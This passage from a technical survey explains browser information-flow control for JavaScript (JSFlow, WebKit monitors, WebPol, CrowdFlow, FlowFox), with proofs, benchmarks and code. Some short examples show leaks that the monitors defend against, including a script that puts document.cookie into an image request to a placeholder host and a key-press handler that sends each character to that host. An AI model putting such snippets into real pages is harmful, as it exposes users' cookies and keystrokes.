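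Two scripts had a different problem. Early in the run, each checked whether a value entered by the user was null, JavaScript's marker for a missing object. The value was secret, so the result of the check was secret too, and JSFlow went on to label much of the later data as secret. But nothing the user did could make the value null, so the check always had the same result and revealed nothing. The programmers had added the checks only to guard against bugs and differences between browsers.

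Upgrading could not help here, because the labels were already too high. Hedin and colleagues instead added declassification annotations, which lower a label. These need much more care than upgrades, because a mistake can release a secret. A better solution, planned for a later version, would track a value's type separately from the value itself. A check for null could then stay public while the visitor's income stayed secret.

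### Checking a secret branch before it runs

In the 2013 experiments, JSFlow used a simple helper that looked ahead for local variables and raised their labels before a secret branch. It removed many false alarms but could not handle object properties. *Value-sensitive Hybrid Information Flow Control for a JavaScript-like Language* (Hedin, Bello and Sabelfeld, 2015) develops the idea much further.

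The 2015 monitor is a hybrid that combines tracking during the run with static analysis. When the script reaches a branch that depends on a secret, the monitor pauses it. A static component then examines both sides of the branch without executing them and raises the label of every location they might write to. The script then continues under the ordinary monitor. In the example above, the component would raise the label of `l` whether `h` was true or false, without any instruction from the programmer.

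"Value-sensitive" means that the static component uses the actual public values in memory at that moment. This matters in code such as the following, which Hedin and colleagues based on a pattern they found in Google Analytics:

```
function makeStore() {
  var data = null;
  function set(d) {data = d;}
  function get() {return data;}
  return {set: set, get: get};
}
var store = makeStore();
if (h) {store.set(true);}
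```

Code outside the function `makeStore` can reach the variable `data` only through `set` and `get`. When `h` is true, the call to `set` writes to `data`, which is labelled public, inside a branch that depends on a secret, so a purely dynamic monitor stops the script. A programmer could not fix this with an upgrade instruction just before the branch, because `data` is out of scope there. The static component looks up the object in `store`, finds the function stored under `set`, examines its body and raises the label of `data`.

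An early `return` needs more analysis. Suppose a function contains `if (h) {return true;} x = 1;`. When the static component finds the `return`, it raises the return label, and the monitor then has it examine the rest of the function. It raises the label of `x` even when the function returns early, because raising it only when execution reaches `x = 1` would reveal `h`.

The static component may never lower a label, and its changes must not depend on secrets. If a secret determines which object a statement writes to, the component leaves the labels unchanged. If it can determine the object but not the property, it raises the labels of the object's structure and all its properties.

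The static component does not have to find every write. If it misses one, the dynamic monitor still applies the no-sensitive-upgrade rule and stops the script, so the error causes a false alarm, not a leak. The component can therefore skip a call to `eval` if it cannot work out the string. A static analysis that had to guarantee security by itself would need to assume that the string could contain any code.

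Hedin and colleagues compared four mechanisms on eight small programs based on patterns they had seen in real code. The programs added properties to objects, changed the scope of variables, returned early, used private variables and called `eval`. The hybrid monitor accepted all eight, JSFlow with its simple helper accepted one, and a purely dynamic monitor accepted none. A static type system, which checks labels before the program runs, accepted three. Hedin and colleagues also proved that the hybrid monitor never stops a program that this type system accepts, though the type system covers only a restricted language without functions or `eval`.

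A static step can also create new false alarms. Consider this program, in which `out` sends a value to the public:

```
l = true;
if (h != h) {l = h;}
out(l);
```

The condition is never true, so the program always sends the same value. A purely dynamic monitor never encounters the assignment and lets the program finish. The hybrid monitor may find the assignment, raise the label of `l` and then block the output. No analysis can recognize every branch that will never run, so some false alarms of this kind are unavoidable.

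Hedin and colleagues chose the eight programs from cases that had caused trouble in their own experiments, so the programs demonstrate the approach on known problems. The monitor was a Haskell prototype for a small part of JavaScript. It did not support exceptions, inherited properties, automatic conversions or the standard library, so it could not run a real page. In their 2016 paper, Hedin and colleagues wrote that the approach could handle all the remaining false alarms they had encountered, and that a full version for JSFlow was under way. It was still unknown whether the approach would remove enough false alarms on pages they had not studied.

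### The hundredfold slowdown

In the 2013 tests, JSFlow was about a hundred times slower than a JavaScript engine with a just-in-time compiler, which translates a script into machine code as the script runs. Hedin and colleagues found JSFlow fast enough for using the test pages by hand, but it would be too slow for pages that do heavy computation.

They object that the figure does not measure how much information-flow tracking slows programs down. JSFlow is an unoptimized interpreter that itself runs in JavaScript, so it would be far slower than an engine that compiles JavaScript even if it ignored labels. This is correct, but it doesn't show that tracking adds little to the running time. The overall figure would be the same if JSFlow without labels were fifty times slower than the compiling engine and tracking doubled the running time, or if it were ten times slower and tracking multiplied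 the running time by ten.

Thiemann later made JSFlow between 1.1 and 1.8 times faster with program specialization, a technique that adapts a general program to input known in advance. Even a 1.8-fold speedup would reduce a hundredfold slowdown only to about 56-fold. The result also does not separate the two sources of slowdown.

Hedin and colleagues name two fairer comparisons but report results for neither. One is to run JSFlow with tracking switched off, which would show how much time labels add in a slow interpreter. This might understate their relative overhead in compiled code. An interpreter already does a lot of work for each addition, so handling a label adds relatively little. Compiled code may need only a few machine instructions, so handling the label could take longer than the addition itself. The other comparison is to build the tracking into an existing browser engine, which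 comes closer to what a user would experience.

### Describing libraries instead of rewriting them

Hand-written library models would remain a problem even if speed and false alarms were solved. In 2016, Hedin and colleagues proposed generating the models from short descriptions, or from static analysis of the library's source code when available. Sjösten (2020) took the first approach in *Information Flow for Web Security and Privacy*, in work with Hedin, Sabelfeld and others.

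In this approach, each library function has an unlabel model, which defines how values lose their labels when they enter the library, and a relabel model, which determines what labels the results get when they leave. The library can be written in a language without label support.

Sjösten and his co-authors use lazy marshaling, which converts each part of a list only when the library uses it. Suppose a script passes a list containing a public number followed by a secret to a function that returns only the first element. If the system removed all the labels at once and combined them, the returned number would be labeled secret even though it is public. With lazy marshaling, the unused secret doesn't affect the result's label.

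The first version, from 2017, could not easily handle libraries in which one function changes data that another later reads, because each value had its own copy of the model's state. The 2018 version keeps this state in shared memory, so a change by one function affects the others. Sjösten tried it on a file-system library, and its security proof was checked in Coq.

EssentialFP, the next system, builds these ideas into JSFlow itself and treats the browser's DOM as a library. It detects browser fingerprinting, in which a script combines details such as screen size and language to recognize a user. It looks for scripts that gather data from many browser functions and send the combination over the network. Sjösten reports that tests on several kinds of page showed a clear difference between fingerprinting and ordinary analytics.

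EssentialFP uses observable tracking, which lets a script continue when labels rise inside secret branches, because the no-sensitive-upgrade rule might stop the script before the whole pattern appeared. Observable tracking also avoids the false alarms that made annotations necessary, but it gives up noninterference, since a branch that does not run can again leak a secret without leaving a label.

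## Monitors inside the WebKit engine: bytecode, events and compiled code

Two research groups avoided much of JSFlow's hundredfold slowdown by building label tracking into WebKit, the open-source browser engine used in Apple's Safari. WebKit compiles a script into bytecode, a list of simple instructions. Its interpreter runs these instructions one at a time, or a just-in-time (JIT) compiler translates them into machine code.

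In 2014, Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues added labels to WebKit's bytecode interpreter (*Information Flow Control in WebKit's JavaScript Bytecode*). Each label is a string of 64 bits, and each bit stands for one web domain. The interpreter combines two labels with a single bitwise "or".

WebKit had 147 bytecode instructions. Bichhawat and colleagues formally modeled 69 of them, since the rest were mostly faster variants, and proved termination-insensitive noninterference for that model. Because the monitor works on bytecode, it checks the code that WebKit runs. If the compiler left out an instruction by mistake, the monitor would still track the faulty program correctly.

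### Finding the end of a secret branch

In source code, braces show where a conditional ends. Bytecode has no braces. The program `if (h) {l = 1;} l = 2;` becomes something like this:

```
1: if h is false, jump to 3
2: l = 1
3: l = 2
```

The list does not mark instruction 3 as outside the conditional. Loops, `break` and `try` compile to similar jumps, so the monitor has to compute when it can lower the pc label again.

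It does this with a small static analysis. When WebKit compiles a function, the monitor builds a control-flow graph, which records the instructions that can follow each instruction. For every branch, it then finds the immediate post-dominator, the first instruction the program is certain to reach whichever way the branch goes. In the list above, that is instruction 3. At the branch, the monitor pushes the label of `h` and the position of instruction 3 onto the pc stack, and it removes this entry when the program reaches that instruction.

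The same method works when a jump carries the effect of a secret past the closing brace:

```
l = 1;
while (1) {
  if (h) {break;}
  l = 0;
  break;
}
```

Here `l` ends up as 1 if `h` is true and 0 otherwise. The assignment `l = 0` is outside the braces of the `if`, but the two paths from the `if` meet only after the loop. The pc therefore stays high during the assignment, so the monitor can treat it as a write that depends on a secret.

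JSFlow handles such jumps with extra labels, which a programmer may have to raise in advance. Using the graph makes those annotations unnecessary. It is also more precise, because any code in the loop before the test of `h` can run in a public context on the first iteration.

The monitor handles code passed to `eval` the same way. WebKit has to compile the string before running it, and the monitor builds a graph for the new code at that point. The new code can't change the graphs of functions already running, so the monitor need not repeat its earlier analysis.

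### Exceptions that leave a function

Exceptions are harder to fit into a graph. If a function throws an exception and does not catch it, control passes to the nearest handler up the call stack. The point where the paths meet again then depends on the caller, so the monitor would have to reanalyze the function for every call.

Bichhawat and colleagues avoid this by adding a synthetic exit node to each function that may throw an uncaught exception. Normal returns and uncaught exceptions both lead to this node, which passes control to the caller or to the right handler. All the graph's edges stay inside one function, so the monitor can build the graph once, at compile time.

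This version of their example has two functions:

```
function g() {
  if (h) {throw "stop";}
}
function f() {
  l = 0;
  try {g();}
  catch (err) {l = 1;}
  return l;
}
```

Without a monitor, `f` returns 1 if `h` is true and 0 if it is false. With the monitor, a call to `f` from a public context goes as follows:

| Step | h is false | h is true |
|---|---|---|
| `f` calls `g` | pushes a low entry that ends at `return l` | the same |
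| `g` tests `h` | raises that entry to high | the same |
| `g` ends | returns normally | throws the exception |
| `f` continues | reaches `return l`, and the pc falls to low | runs the handler with a high pc |
| Outcome | returns a low 0 | breaks the no-sensitive-upgrade rule at `l = 1` |

In the second step, the `if` in `g` has the exit node as its post-dominator, so its paths meet outside `g`. The monitor already has an entry for that place on the stack, so it raises the label on that entry instead of adding a new one. The high label therefore still applies when the exception handler runs.

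Many JavaScript instructions can throw an exception. If each had an edge to the exit node, a secret branch would often keep the pc high until the end of the function. The monitor therefore leaves out the exit node when no caller on the call stack has an active handler. An exception would then end the program, which termination-insensitive noninterference allows as long as the attacker cannot see the error message.

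### A delayed check on assignments

A strict no-sensitive-upgrade rule would work poorly on bytecode because WebKit's compiler often puts assignments inside branches even when the program never uses the assigned values. The rule would stop the program unnecessarily at each of these assignments. Bichhawat and colleagues therefore adapted Austin and Flanagan's permissive-upgrade variant, which marks the variable as partially leaked instead of stopping the program.

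They changed the point at which the program has to stop. Suppose that `l` is a local variable and `obj` an ordinary object that the attacker can read:

```
l = 0;
if (h) {l = 1;}
obj.a = l;
```

Austin and Flanagan's version lets both runs finish. If `h` is true, `obj.a` receives a 1 marked as partially leaked. If `h` is false, `obj.a` receives an ordinary public 0, and the monitor cannot determine that the other run would have stored a marked value. An attacker who can read the object through another part of the browser may see that 0 and learn the secret.

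The new rule, which Bichhawat and colleagues call the deferred no-sensitive-upgrade check, stops the program before it stores a partially leaked value in an object or branches on one. In the example, the run with `h` true stops at the third line, so every run that finishes leaves 0 in `obj.a`.

Marked values may still move between local variables, because WebKit keeps these in registers that scripts from other parties cannot read directly. This distinction between variables and objects depends on WebKit's implementation, whereas the ECMAScript standard describes variable scopes as if they were objects.

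### The measured cost in bytecode

Bichhawat and colleagues compared their monitor with the same WebKit interpreter without labels, running in Safari 6.0 with the JIT compiler off in both cases. They tested a basic version of the monitor and an optimized one, which does not label a function's local variables until the function reads an object property whose label differs from the pc.

| Test | Basic overhead | Optimized overhead |
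|---|---|---|
| SunSpider, a set of short JavaScript programs | 121% | 45% |
| JSBench, a benchmark derived from real websites | about 38% | about 38% |
| First load of nine popular websites | about 29% | about 29% |

The optimization helped little on real sites, probably because their scripts use objects more often than the SunSpider programs do. The website figures include only the time spent running JavaScript. Bichhawat and colleagues consider the overhead negligible compared with the time needed to fetch and display a page.

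The choice of baseline matters most for heavy computation. WebKit's JIT compiler made the SunSpider programs much faster, so a user who turned it off to use the monitor would see a slowdown of more than 45%. On the nine websites, though, the JIT compiler made the plain browser slower, because the scripts that run when a page loads were too short for compiling them to save time.

In all these tests, the monitor ignored violations and let the scripts continue. The figures therefore measure the overhead of complete runs, but do not show how many of the nine sites would have worked with enforcement on. The 2014 version also did not yet label the browser's native functions, including the DOM, which is why one SunSpider test, on regular expressions, showed almost no overhead.

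### A leak through event dispatch

Most of a page's code runs in event handlers, functions that the browser calls in response to events such as clicks. The 2014 proof covers only one call into the interpreter at a time. *Information Flow Control for Event Handling and the DOM in Web Browsers* (Rajani, Bichhawat and colleagues, 2015) extends the monitor to the DOM and to the browser's choice of which handlers to run.

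When a user clicks on an element, the browser also runs certain handlers on the elements that contain it. It first works out the propagation path, the chain of elements from the one clicked to the top of the page. It then runs handlers in three phases:

1. In the capture phase, it goes down the path from the top of the page to the element's parent.
2. In the target phase, it runs the handlers of the element itself.
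3. In the bubble phase, it goes back up from the parent to the top.

A script can use this procedure to copy a secret. In the following example, slightly shortened from the paper, `a` and `b` are page elements and `sec` is secret:

```
pub = false;
a.addEventListener("click", aCk, true);
b.addEventListener("click", bCk, false);
if (sec) {a.appendChild(b);}
b.dispatchEvent("click");
function aCk() {pub = true;}
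function bCk() {}
```

The value `true` in the second line registers `aCk` for the capture phase. The script places `b` inside `a` only if `sec` is true, and then triggers a click on `b` in either case. If `sec` is true, the browser runs `aCk` on its way down to `b`, and `aCk` sets `pub` to true. If `sec` is false, `a` is not on the path, so `aCk` never runs.

The click happens outside the `if`, so a monitor that tracked only the script's own branches would run `aCk` with a low pc. `pub` would then hold a copy of `sec` with a low label. The relevant branch occurs in the browser's code, when the browser looks for the parent of `b`.

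Rajani and colleagues close the leak by labeling each link between two elements with the pc at the time the script creates it. When an event occurs, the browser combines the labels of all the links on the propagation path, and every handler for that event runs in a context at least as secret as the result. Here the link between `a` and `b` is high:

| | sec is false | sec is true |
|---|---|---|
| Propagation path | does not include `a` | includes `a`, through a high link |
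| `aCk` | does not run | runs with a high pc |
| `pub = true` | never runs | the monitor stops the script |
| Final `pub` | false | no result |

The table assumes that the links were already high before the `if`. Otherwise the monitor would stop the script earlier, at `appendChild`, because changing a public link while control flow depends on a secret breaks the no-sensitive-upgrade rule.

### Paused handlers and hidden tables

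Rajani and colleagues also found that a handler can be interrupted before it finishes. In Chrome 40, a click handler that opened an alert box had to wait until the user closed the box, and the browser could run a window-resize handler in the meantime.

Suppose one handler sets `pub` to true, pauses only if `sec` is true, and then sets `pub` to false. A second handler is waiting to copy `pub` into `conf`. If the first handler pauses, the second copies true; otherwise, it copies false.

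Running the second handler with the high pc of the paused one prevents the leak only if `conf` starts low, because the monitor then stops the write. If `conf` starts high, the write succeeds and leaves `conf` true and labelled high. In the run without a pause, the second handler starts later with a low pc and leaves `conf` false and labelled low. An attacker can distinguish the two outcomes by checking whether `conf` is readable.

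The extended monitor gives each handler a minimum label based on the context in which the script registered it. During a pause in a secret context, the browser may run only handlers whose label is at least as secret, and the others must wait. Programmers do not have to supply these labels.

Live collections are simpler to handle in WebKit than in JSFlow, which keeps a label on each query for them. WebKit recalculates a collection by walking the DOM tree, so the labels on the links between elements are enough to protect the result.

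To speed up `getElementById`, WebKit keeps a table of elements indexed by id, which can leak information if its entries are labelled incorrectly. Suppose a script puts element `c` inside element `b` in a secret branch, and later adds `b` to the page in a public context. WebKit then adds `c` to the table as well. If the entry were labelled only with the current low pc, a search for `c` would return a public result that reveals whether the secret branch ran. The entry's label must therefore also include the label of the link between `b` and `c`. This leak can't be found by reading the DOM standard, because the table isn't part of it.

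Rajani and colleagues proved noninterference for their model of events and the DOM, assuming the monitor for ordinary JavaScript is sound. The proof does not cover leaks through timing or termination. The extension added about 2,300 lines of code to the original 4,500.

They again switched off the JIT compiler and ignored violations when measuring speed. The average overhead was about 71% on Dromaeo, a benchmark that repeats DOM operations. It was about 32% on the front pages of the ten most popular websites, with a worst case of around 60%. The page tests involved no user interaction, so they did not measure how the new rules affect clicks or typing.

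### Rules written by the site: WebPol

A monitor needs a policy that specifies which data is sensitive. With *WebPol* (Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues, 2017), the site's developer writes this policy in ordinary JavaScript. Data can have one of three kinds of label. Public data may go anywhere, data labeled with a domain may go only to that domain and its subdomains, and local data may not leave the browser. `HOST` stands for the page's own domain.

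Consider a shop that shows its prices in US dollars and uses a script from currConv.com to convert them. The script reads the amount and the currency the customer has chosen, asks its own server for the exchange rate and writes the converted price into the page. It has to send out the name of the currency, but it has no need to send the amount. The shop can state this in one line:

```
document.getElementById("amt").setLabel("HOST");
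```

The request for the exchange rate contains only the name of the currency, which is public, so the monitor allows it. The script then multiplies the rate by the amount. The result has the shop's label, and the script can still display it on the page. An honest converter therefore needs no changes, but if the script tries to put the amount into another request to currConv.com, the monitor blocks that request.

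A second function, `setContext`, hides that an event happened. A site could use it to let an analytics company learn that a visitor clicked somewhere in a section, but not how many times. These policies are event handlers that run before all others. The browser accepts them only from the page's own HTML, so a third-party script cannot install a more permissive policy.

Bichhawat and colleagues tried WebPol on a password-strength checker, passwordmeter.com, and on a bank's login page with analytics scripts. The times below are for running JavaScript:

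| Page | No tracking | Tracking only | Tracking and policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Password checker | 79.5 ms | 115.5 ms | 126 ms |
| Bank login | 273.4 ms | 375.1 ms | 386.1 ms |

Most of the extra time came from tracking. Writing the rules required some knowledge of the scripts. On the password site, for example, the strength score depends on the password, so Bichhawat and colleagues had to add four lines to let the script write the score into the page. WebPol also trusts the site completely, so it would not have stopped the loan calculator that passed its visitors' figures to Google Analytics through its own server.

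### The Irvine interpreter

Kerschbaumer, Hennigan and colleagues at the University of California, Irvine, put speed ahead of a complete guarantee. *Towards Precise and Efficient Information Flow Control in Web Browsers* (2013) presents their WebKit interpreter, which doubles each JavaScript value from 64 to 128 bits and stores the label in the second half. A label can represent up to 63 domains directly, and the interpreter uses a slower method for pages with more.

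The interpreter tracks explicit flows and adds the pc label to any value a script writes inside a secret branch. It does not apply the no-sensitive-upgrade rule or analyze branches that do not run, so it would miss the leak in Hedin and colleagues' three-line program with `l` and `t`.

Before sending a network request, the browser compares the label of the address with the domain that will receive the request. If they differ, it records a violation and notifies the user. The tests used copies of ten web pages with known security holes. In a copy of an Amazon page, which loaded code from eight origins, the browser detected an injected script that tried to send out the user's keystrokes.

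They also had a program visit the 500 most popular websites, spend a minute on each and fill in a form where it found one. They recorded 8,764 violations on 433 of the sites. Most of these may not have been thefts, because the browser counts any difference between the label and the destination as a violation. A company that keeps its images on a second domain could trigger one just by sending data there. Kerschbaumer and colleagues concluded that only site authors could say which flows were acceptable. WebPol later let site authors provide that information.

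On SunSpider, the tracking interpreter was 82.82% slower than WebKit's ordinary interpreter. On Dromaeo its overhead was only 5.43%, compared with 71% for the monitor by Rajani and colleagues. The two DOM figures were measured on different machines and versions of WebKit, and the systems do different amounts of work. The Irvine browser labels elements and their attributes, while the monitor by Rajani and colleagues also labels every link between elements and checks each change to a link.

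The group also compared its interpreter with WebKit's JIT compiler, separating the slowdown due to interpretation from the slowdown due to tracking, which the JSFlow figure had combined. The ordinary interpreter took about 3.5 times as long as compiled code. Tracking multiplied that time by 1.8, so the complete system took about 6.3 times as long as compiled code.

### Tracking in compiled code

The group moved the tracking into the compiler to remove the larger of these two factors. Kerschbaumer, Hennigan and colleagues describe the result in *Information Flow Tracking meets Just-In-Time Compilation*. They believed it was the first JIT compiler for a dynamically typed language that tracks information flow.

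The design stores each label in spare bits of the existing 64-bit values, because larger values would have slowed the compiled code. Whole numbers already had 16 unused bits, and limiting the memory for objects to 4 gigabytes freed 16 bits in object references. A label can therefore name 16 domains. Numbers with a fractional part use all 64 bits and leave no space for a label, so the compiler treats each one as if every domain on the page had influenced it. This avoids missed leaks but can cause false alarms.

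To add two whole numbers, the compiled code does the following:

1. It combines the labels of the two numbers.
2. It adds the current pc label, of which it keeps a copy in a place it can reach quickly.
3. It clears all the bits that do not belong to the label.
4. It adds the numbers.
5. It attaches the label to the sum.

In the simplified machine code that the group published, this takes eight instructions, only one of which does the addition.

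Even so, the average overhead was 73% across the SunSpider, V8 and Kraken benchmark suites. The baseline this time was WebKit's unmodified JIT compiler, so this figure is much closer to what a user would notice than the interpreter's 82.82%. On 100 randomly chosen websites, the compiled code found the same flows as the group's interpreter.

The compiler inserts instructions that raise the program-counter (pc) label at a branch and lower it afterwards. If a `break` runs in a branch that depends on secret data, these instructions keep the pc label high for the rest of the function. If the `break` does not run, they lower the label at the end of the `if`. This leaves a gap in the enforcement, because the label after the `if` depends on whether the `break` ran, and therefore on the secret.

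In the earlier example with `while`, this means that `l = 0` runs with a low pc when `h` is false. Suppose the loop is inside a function and `l` is a global variable. Code that reads `l` after the function ends gets either 1 or 0, labelled low in both cases, and this value reveals `h`. The monitor of Bichhawat and colleagues catches this program because it keeps the pc high until the two paths meet.

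Kerschbaumer and colleagues deliberately left this gap because they wanted to study only speed, and they objected that the known remedies either stop harmless scripts or label far too much data as secret. The 73% overhead is therefore for a weaker form of tracking, and a compiler that also enforced noninterference would have to make more checks.

### CrowdFlow: sharing the work among visitors

The Irvine group's other idea was to have each visitor's browser track only part of a page's code. *CrowdFlow*, by Kerschbaumer, Hennigan and colleagues, describes a browser that normally runs scripts in a fast mode, which passes on labels only when a script copies a value directly, as in `a = b;`. At each function call, the browser may switch at random to a slower mode with full tracking.

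If the slower mode finds a value that mixes data from two domains, the browser may keep full tracking on from then on. Otherwise it goes back to the fast mode when the function ends. The flows covered in each mode compare with those of the other systems as follows:

| System | Direct copies | Computed values | Writes in secret branches that run | Secret branches that do not run |
|---|---|---|---|---|
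| Bichhawat and colleagues, bytecode monitor | yes | yes | yes | yes |
| Irvine interpreter and compiler | yes | yes | yes | no |
| CrowdFlow, full tracking | yes | yes | yes | no |
| CrowdFlow, fast mode | yes | no | no | no |

With a 5% chance of switching at each call, the overhead over WebKit's ordinary interpreter was 27.84% on SunSpider and 32.05% on V8. With full tracking at every call, it was about 170%. The saving is smaller relative to the group's earlier interpreter, which always tracked everything and had an overhead of 82.82% on SunSpider.

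To measure how much CrowdFlow misses, the group sent five simulated users to the same 500 websites where full tracking had found 8,764 violations.

| Simulated user | New violations | Running total |
|---|---|---|
| A | 5,480 | 5,480 |
| B | 1,957 | 7,437 |
| C | 903 | 8,340 |
| D | 173 | 8,513 |
| E | 203 | 8,716 |

Together, the five users found 99.45% of the violations that full tracking had found. This figure leaves out any leaks through branches that did not run, because full tracking does not detect them.

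User A alone found about 63%, although the browser sampled only 5% of calls, partly because scripts call the same functions repeatedly. Across the 500 sites, the average function ran about 34 times, which gives the browser an over 80% chance of sampling at least one call. An attacker's function that runs just once, for example to build the address for the stolen data, would usually escape, because the chance that the browser samples that call may be only one in 20.

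The 99.45% therefore measures what a crowd can discover about a website, and no individual visitor gets that level of protection. User A's browser missed more than a third of the violations, and any real secrets among them would have leaked. CrowdFlow also does not block the leaks it finds. It reports them to a service that keeps a list of malicious addresses, similar to the lists browsers use to warn of fraudulent websites. These reports can help protect later visitors, but not the people whose leaked data revealed the attack.

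Kerschbaumer and colleagues said that CrowdFlow was not meant to stop an attack on one particular person, because there would be no crowd of users to detect it. They expected that if CrowdFlow became widely used, attackers would write scripts that leaked data only while full tracking was off. A script might recognize full tracking by timing its own code, which runs slower in that mode. They suggested labeling the clock too, so that the browser could track what a script does with the time.

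## FlowFox: running each script once per secrecy level

FlowFox, which De Groef and colleagues built in 2012 by modifying Firefox 8.0.1, runs each script twice. The high run receives the secrets, but all public output comes from the low run, which never receives them. This technique is called secure multi-execution, and Devriese and Piessens had already tested it in Firefox's JavaScript engine, SpiderMonkey, without connecting it to a full browser. JSFlow and the WebKit monitors follow a single run of a script, so they need extra rules for the branches that this run does not take.

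### Four rules for input and output

Both runs execute the same code. They differ only where the script exchanges data with the world outside it. Reading a cookie is an input, for example, and requesting an image is an output. The policy gives each of these operations a level, low or high, and four rules then apply:

1. The browser performs each input or output only in the run at the same level, so it never performs one twice.
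2. A run skips every output at the other level.
3. If the low run reaches a high input, it skips the input and continues with a default value of a suitable type.
4. If the high run reaches a low input, it waits for the low run to perform that input and then reuses the result.

De Groef and colleagues illustrate the rules with a script that puts the page's cookies into an image address and then uses the width of the image to arrange the page:

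```
var url = "http://host/image.jpg?=" + document.cookie;
var i = new Image(); i.src = url;
if (i.width > 50) { /* change the layout */ }
```

Here the policy treats reading the cookie as a high input. Setting `i.src` is a low output, because it makes the browser request the image, and reading `i.width` is a low input. Suppose the cookie is `id=42` and the image is 100 pixels wide:

| Step | Low run | High run |
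|---|---|---|
| Read `document.cookie` | gets an empty string (rule 3) | gets `id=42` |
| Build `url` | the address has no cookie in it | the address contains `id=42` |
| Set `i.src` | the browser requests the image | skips the request (rule 2) |
| Read `i.width` | gets 100 from the browser | reuses the 100 (rule 4) |
| Test `i.width > 50` | true | true |

The server receives a request for the image, but the place for the cookie in the address is empty.

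The low run can't leak a secret because it never receives one. If the script branches on the cookie, the low run branches on the empty string instead, so it takes the same path whatever the real cookie is. FlowFox therefore needs no pc label, no search for the end of a secret branch and no upgrade instructions.

The method also preserves the behavior of harmless scripts. If a script's public output doesn't depend on secrets, replacing those secrets with default values can't change that output. Devriese and Piessens proved this property, which they call precision, for runs that finish in a small model language. Monitors that rely on the no-sensitive-upgrade rule lack it.

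The fourth rule also keeps the user from having to answer the same question twice. This would happen if both runs called `window.confirm`, the browser function that shows the user a question and returns the answer.

### Why FlowFox repeats only the scripts

Capizzi and colleagues had applied a similar idea, called shadow executions, to Firefox in 2008. They ran the entire browser twice, with one process for secret data and one for public data. Bielova and colleagues later worked out the theory for programs that respond to events and tried it on a simple browser model written in OCaml. In both designs, each copy of the browser has its own copy of the page.

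Running the whole browser once per secrecy level is easier to build, because the operating system can already run two processes and the security mechanism only has to control their access to files, the network and the screen. But the mechanism then has too little information to label data well. The operating system can detect a key press, but not which tab or text field it was for. De Groef and colleagues give the example of a user typing an e-mail into a webmail page. The mechanism cannot determine which site the text belongs to, so a script on the page could send it to any site with which the browser has an active session in another tab.

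FlowFox uses a single browser and a single copy of the page. It treats every call from a script to the browser as an output (the function and its arguments) followed by an input (the result), so a policy can refer to a particular browser function or even a particular argument. The drawbacks are that De Groef and colleagues had to change code in many parts of Firefox, and that policies become more complex because a browser offers scripts far more functions than an operating system offers programs.

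### Two versions of each object, one version of the page

The changes came to about 1,400 lines of C and C++. SpiderMonkey has a record for each property of an object, and FlowFox adds a level to that record. An object can then have two properties with the same name at different levels, and each run can access only the properties at its own level. For example, `a.b` might be an object in the low run and a number in the high run.

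The engine also stores the level of the current run. A loop around the code that compiles and executes scripts runs each script with this level set to low, then again with it set to high. A string passed to `eval` runs at the level of the run that built it.

Calls to the browser pass through XPConnect, a layer of Firefox that converts JavaScript values into the C++ values the rest of the browser uses. FlowFox intercepts each call there, looks up its level in the policy and compares it with the level of the run:

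| Level of the call | In the low run | In the high run |
|---|---|---|
| Low | makes the call and stores the result in a cache | takes the result from the cache |
| High | returns the default value | makes the call |

Event handlers run later, when the loop has long finished, so FlowFox stores with each handler the level of the run that registered it. If an event is low, both runs register a handler, and when the event occurs the low handler runs first and the high one second. If the policy makes an event high, registering a handler for it is a high call, which the low run skips. Take this handler for key presses:

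```
function handler(e) {
  new Image().src = "http://host/?=" + e.charCode;
}
```

If key presses are high, only the high run registers the handler. When the user presses a key, the handler receives the real character but skips the image request, so the server at `host` does not even learn that the user pressed a key.

### Policy rules and default values

A rule in a FlowFox policy gives the level of a browser function and the default value for runs that may not call it. This one protects cookies:

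```
R1[document.cookie] : true → H ↪ ""
```

`R1` is the name of the rule, and the square brackets contain the function or property it covers. The condition `true` means the rule always applies. `H` is the level, and the empty string at the end is the default value. A rule can have several conditions, each with its own level, and FlowFox uses the first one that holds. Calls without a rule are low, so with an empty policy FlowFox gives scripts the same access as an ordinary browser.

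A policy's conditions can depend on the arguments of a call. For example, a policy can label network requests high if they go to the page's own server and low otherwise. The high run then sends the requests to the page's server, with real data in them, and the low run sends the rest. A script can therefore send a cookie only to the site that set it.

Secrets can reach only calls that the policy labels high, so even simple policies are harder to write than they look. De Groef and colleagues describe a script that reads the user's preferred background color from a cookie. If the policy labels only the cookie high, the low run makes the call that sets the background, but it doesn't have the color. The policy must label that call high too.

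Other rules follow the same pattern. Some scripts find out which sites a user has visited by checking whether links appear in the color for visited pages. A policy can make the color high and give the low run the color of an unvisited link. For scripts that record mouse movements, it can give the low run default coordinates of 0. De Groef and colleagues also wrote a rule for Tynt, the clipboard service that Hedin and colleagues had studied. It makes the selected text high, so Tynt's server receives an empty string when a reader copies a passage.

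They did not expect users to write such rules. Browser vendors could supply them as privacy profiles, or a website could send rules for its own data. But even experts can easily make mistakes. *Client- and Server-Side Security Technologies for JavaScript Web Applications* (De Groef, 2016) prints JavaScript code for the rule about requests to the page's own server. Its test returns true if the address does not contain the site's name, so the printed policy labels requests to other sites as high, which would let a script send them real secrets. This is probably only a slip in the listing, but FlowFox would enforce such a policy without any sign of an error.

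### Screenshots and recorded visits

FlowFox changes how every script runs, so De Groef and colleagues checked that websites still worked. A crawler opened the home pages of Alexa's 500 most popular sites in two ordinary copies of Firefox and one copy of FlowFox. The policy labelled only cookie reads as high. The crawler took a screenshot in each browser after the page had loaded.

Many pages look different each time they load, so a direct comparison would have produced false differences. The crawler first compared the two Firefox screenshots and masked every pixel that differed. This removed slideshows, advertisements and the time of day. The crawler then compared FlowFox with Firefox on the remaining pixels. The masks were usually small, and so were any remaining differences.

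De Groef and colleagues checked the pages with larger differences by hand. Some content was missing or in a different position. In other cases, one browser had received an item from the network before the other, or an image had changed in a way the mask did not cover. One site violated the policy, but FlowFox displayed it correctly with a suitable default value.

A home page that nobody clicks on exercises only part of a site's code, so they also recorded visits by logged-in users and replayed them in FlowFox. These covered six kinds of site:

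| Site | What the user did |
|---|---|
| Google | chose a suggested search term and waited for the results |
| Facebook | sent a private message to a friend |
| Yahoo! | wrote and sent an e-mail |
| Wikipedia | searched for an article and opened it |
| Blogspot | wrote and saved a blog post |
| Amazon | put a book in the shopping cart and removed it |

In every case, a user could not have told FlowFox from Firefox. Two more recordings, on the sites of Microsoft and the newspaper *The Sun*, triggered scripts that track clicks and selected text. Under a policy covering this data, the tracking companies received default values, and the pages worked as before.

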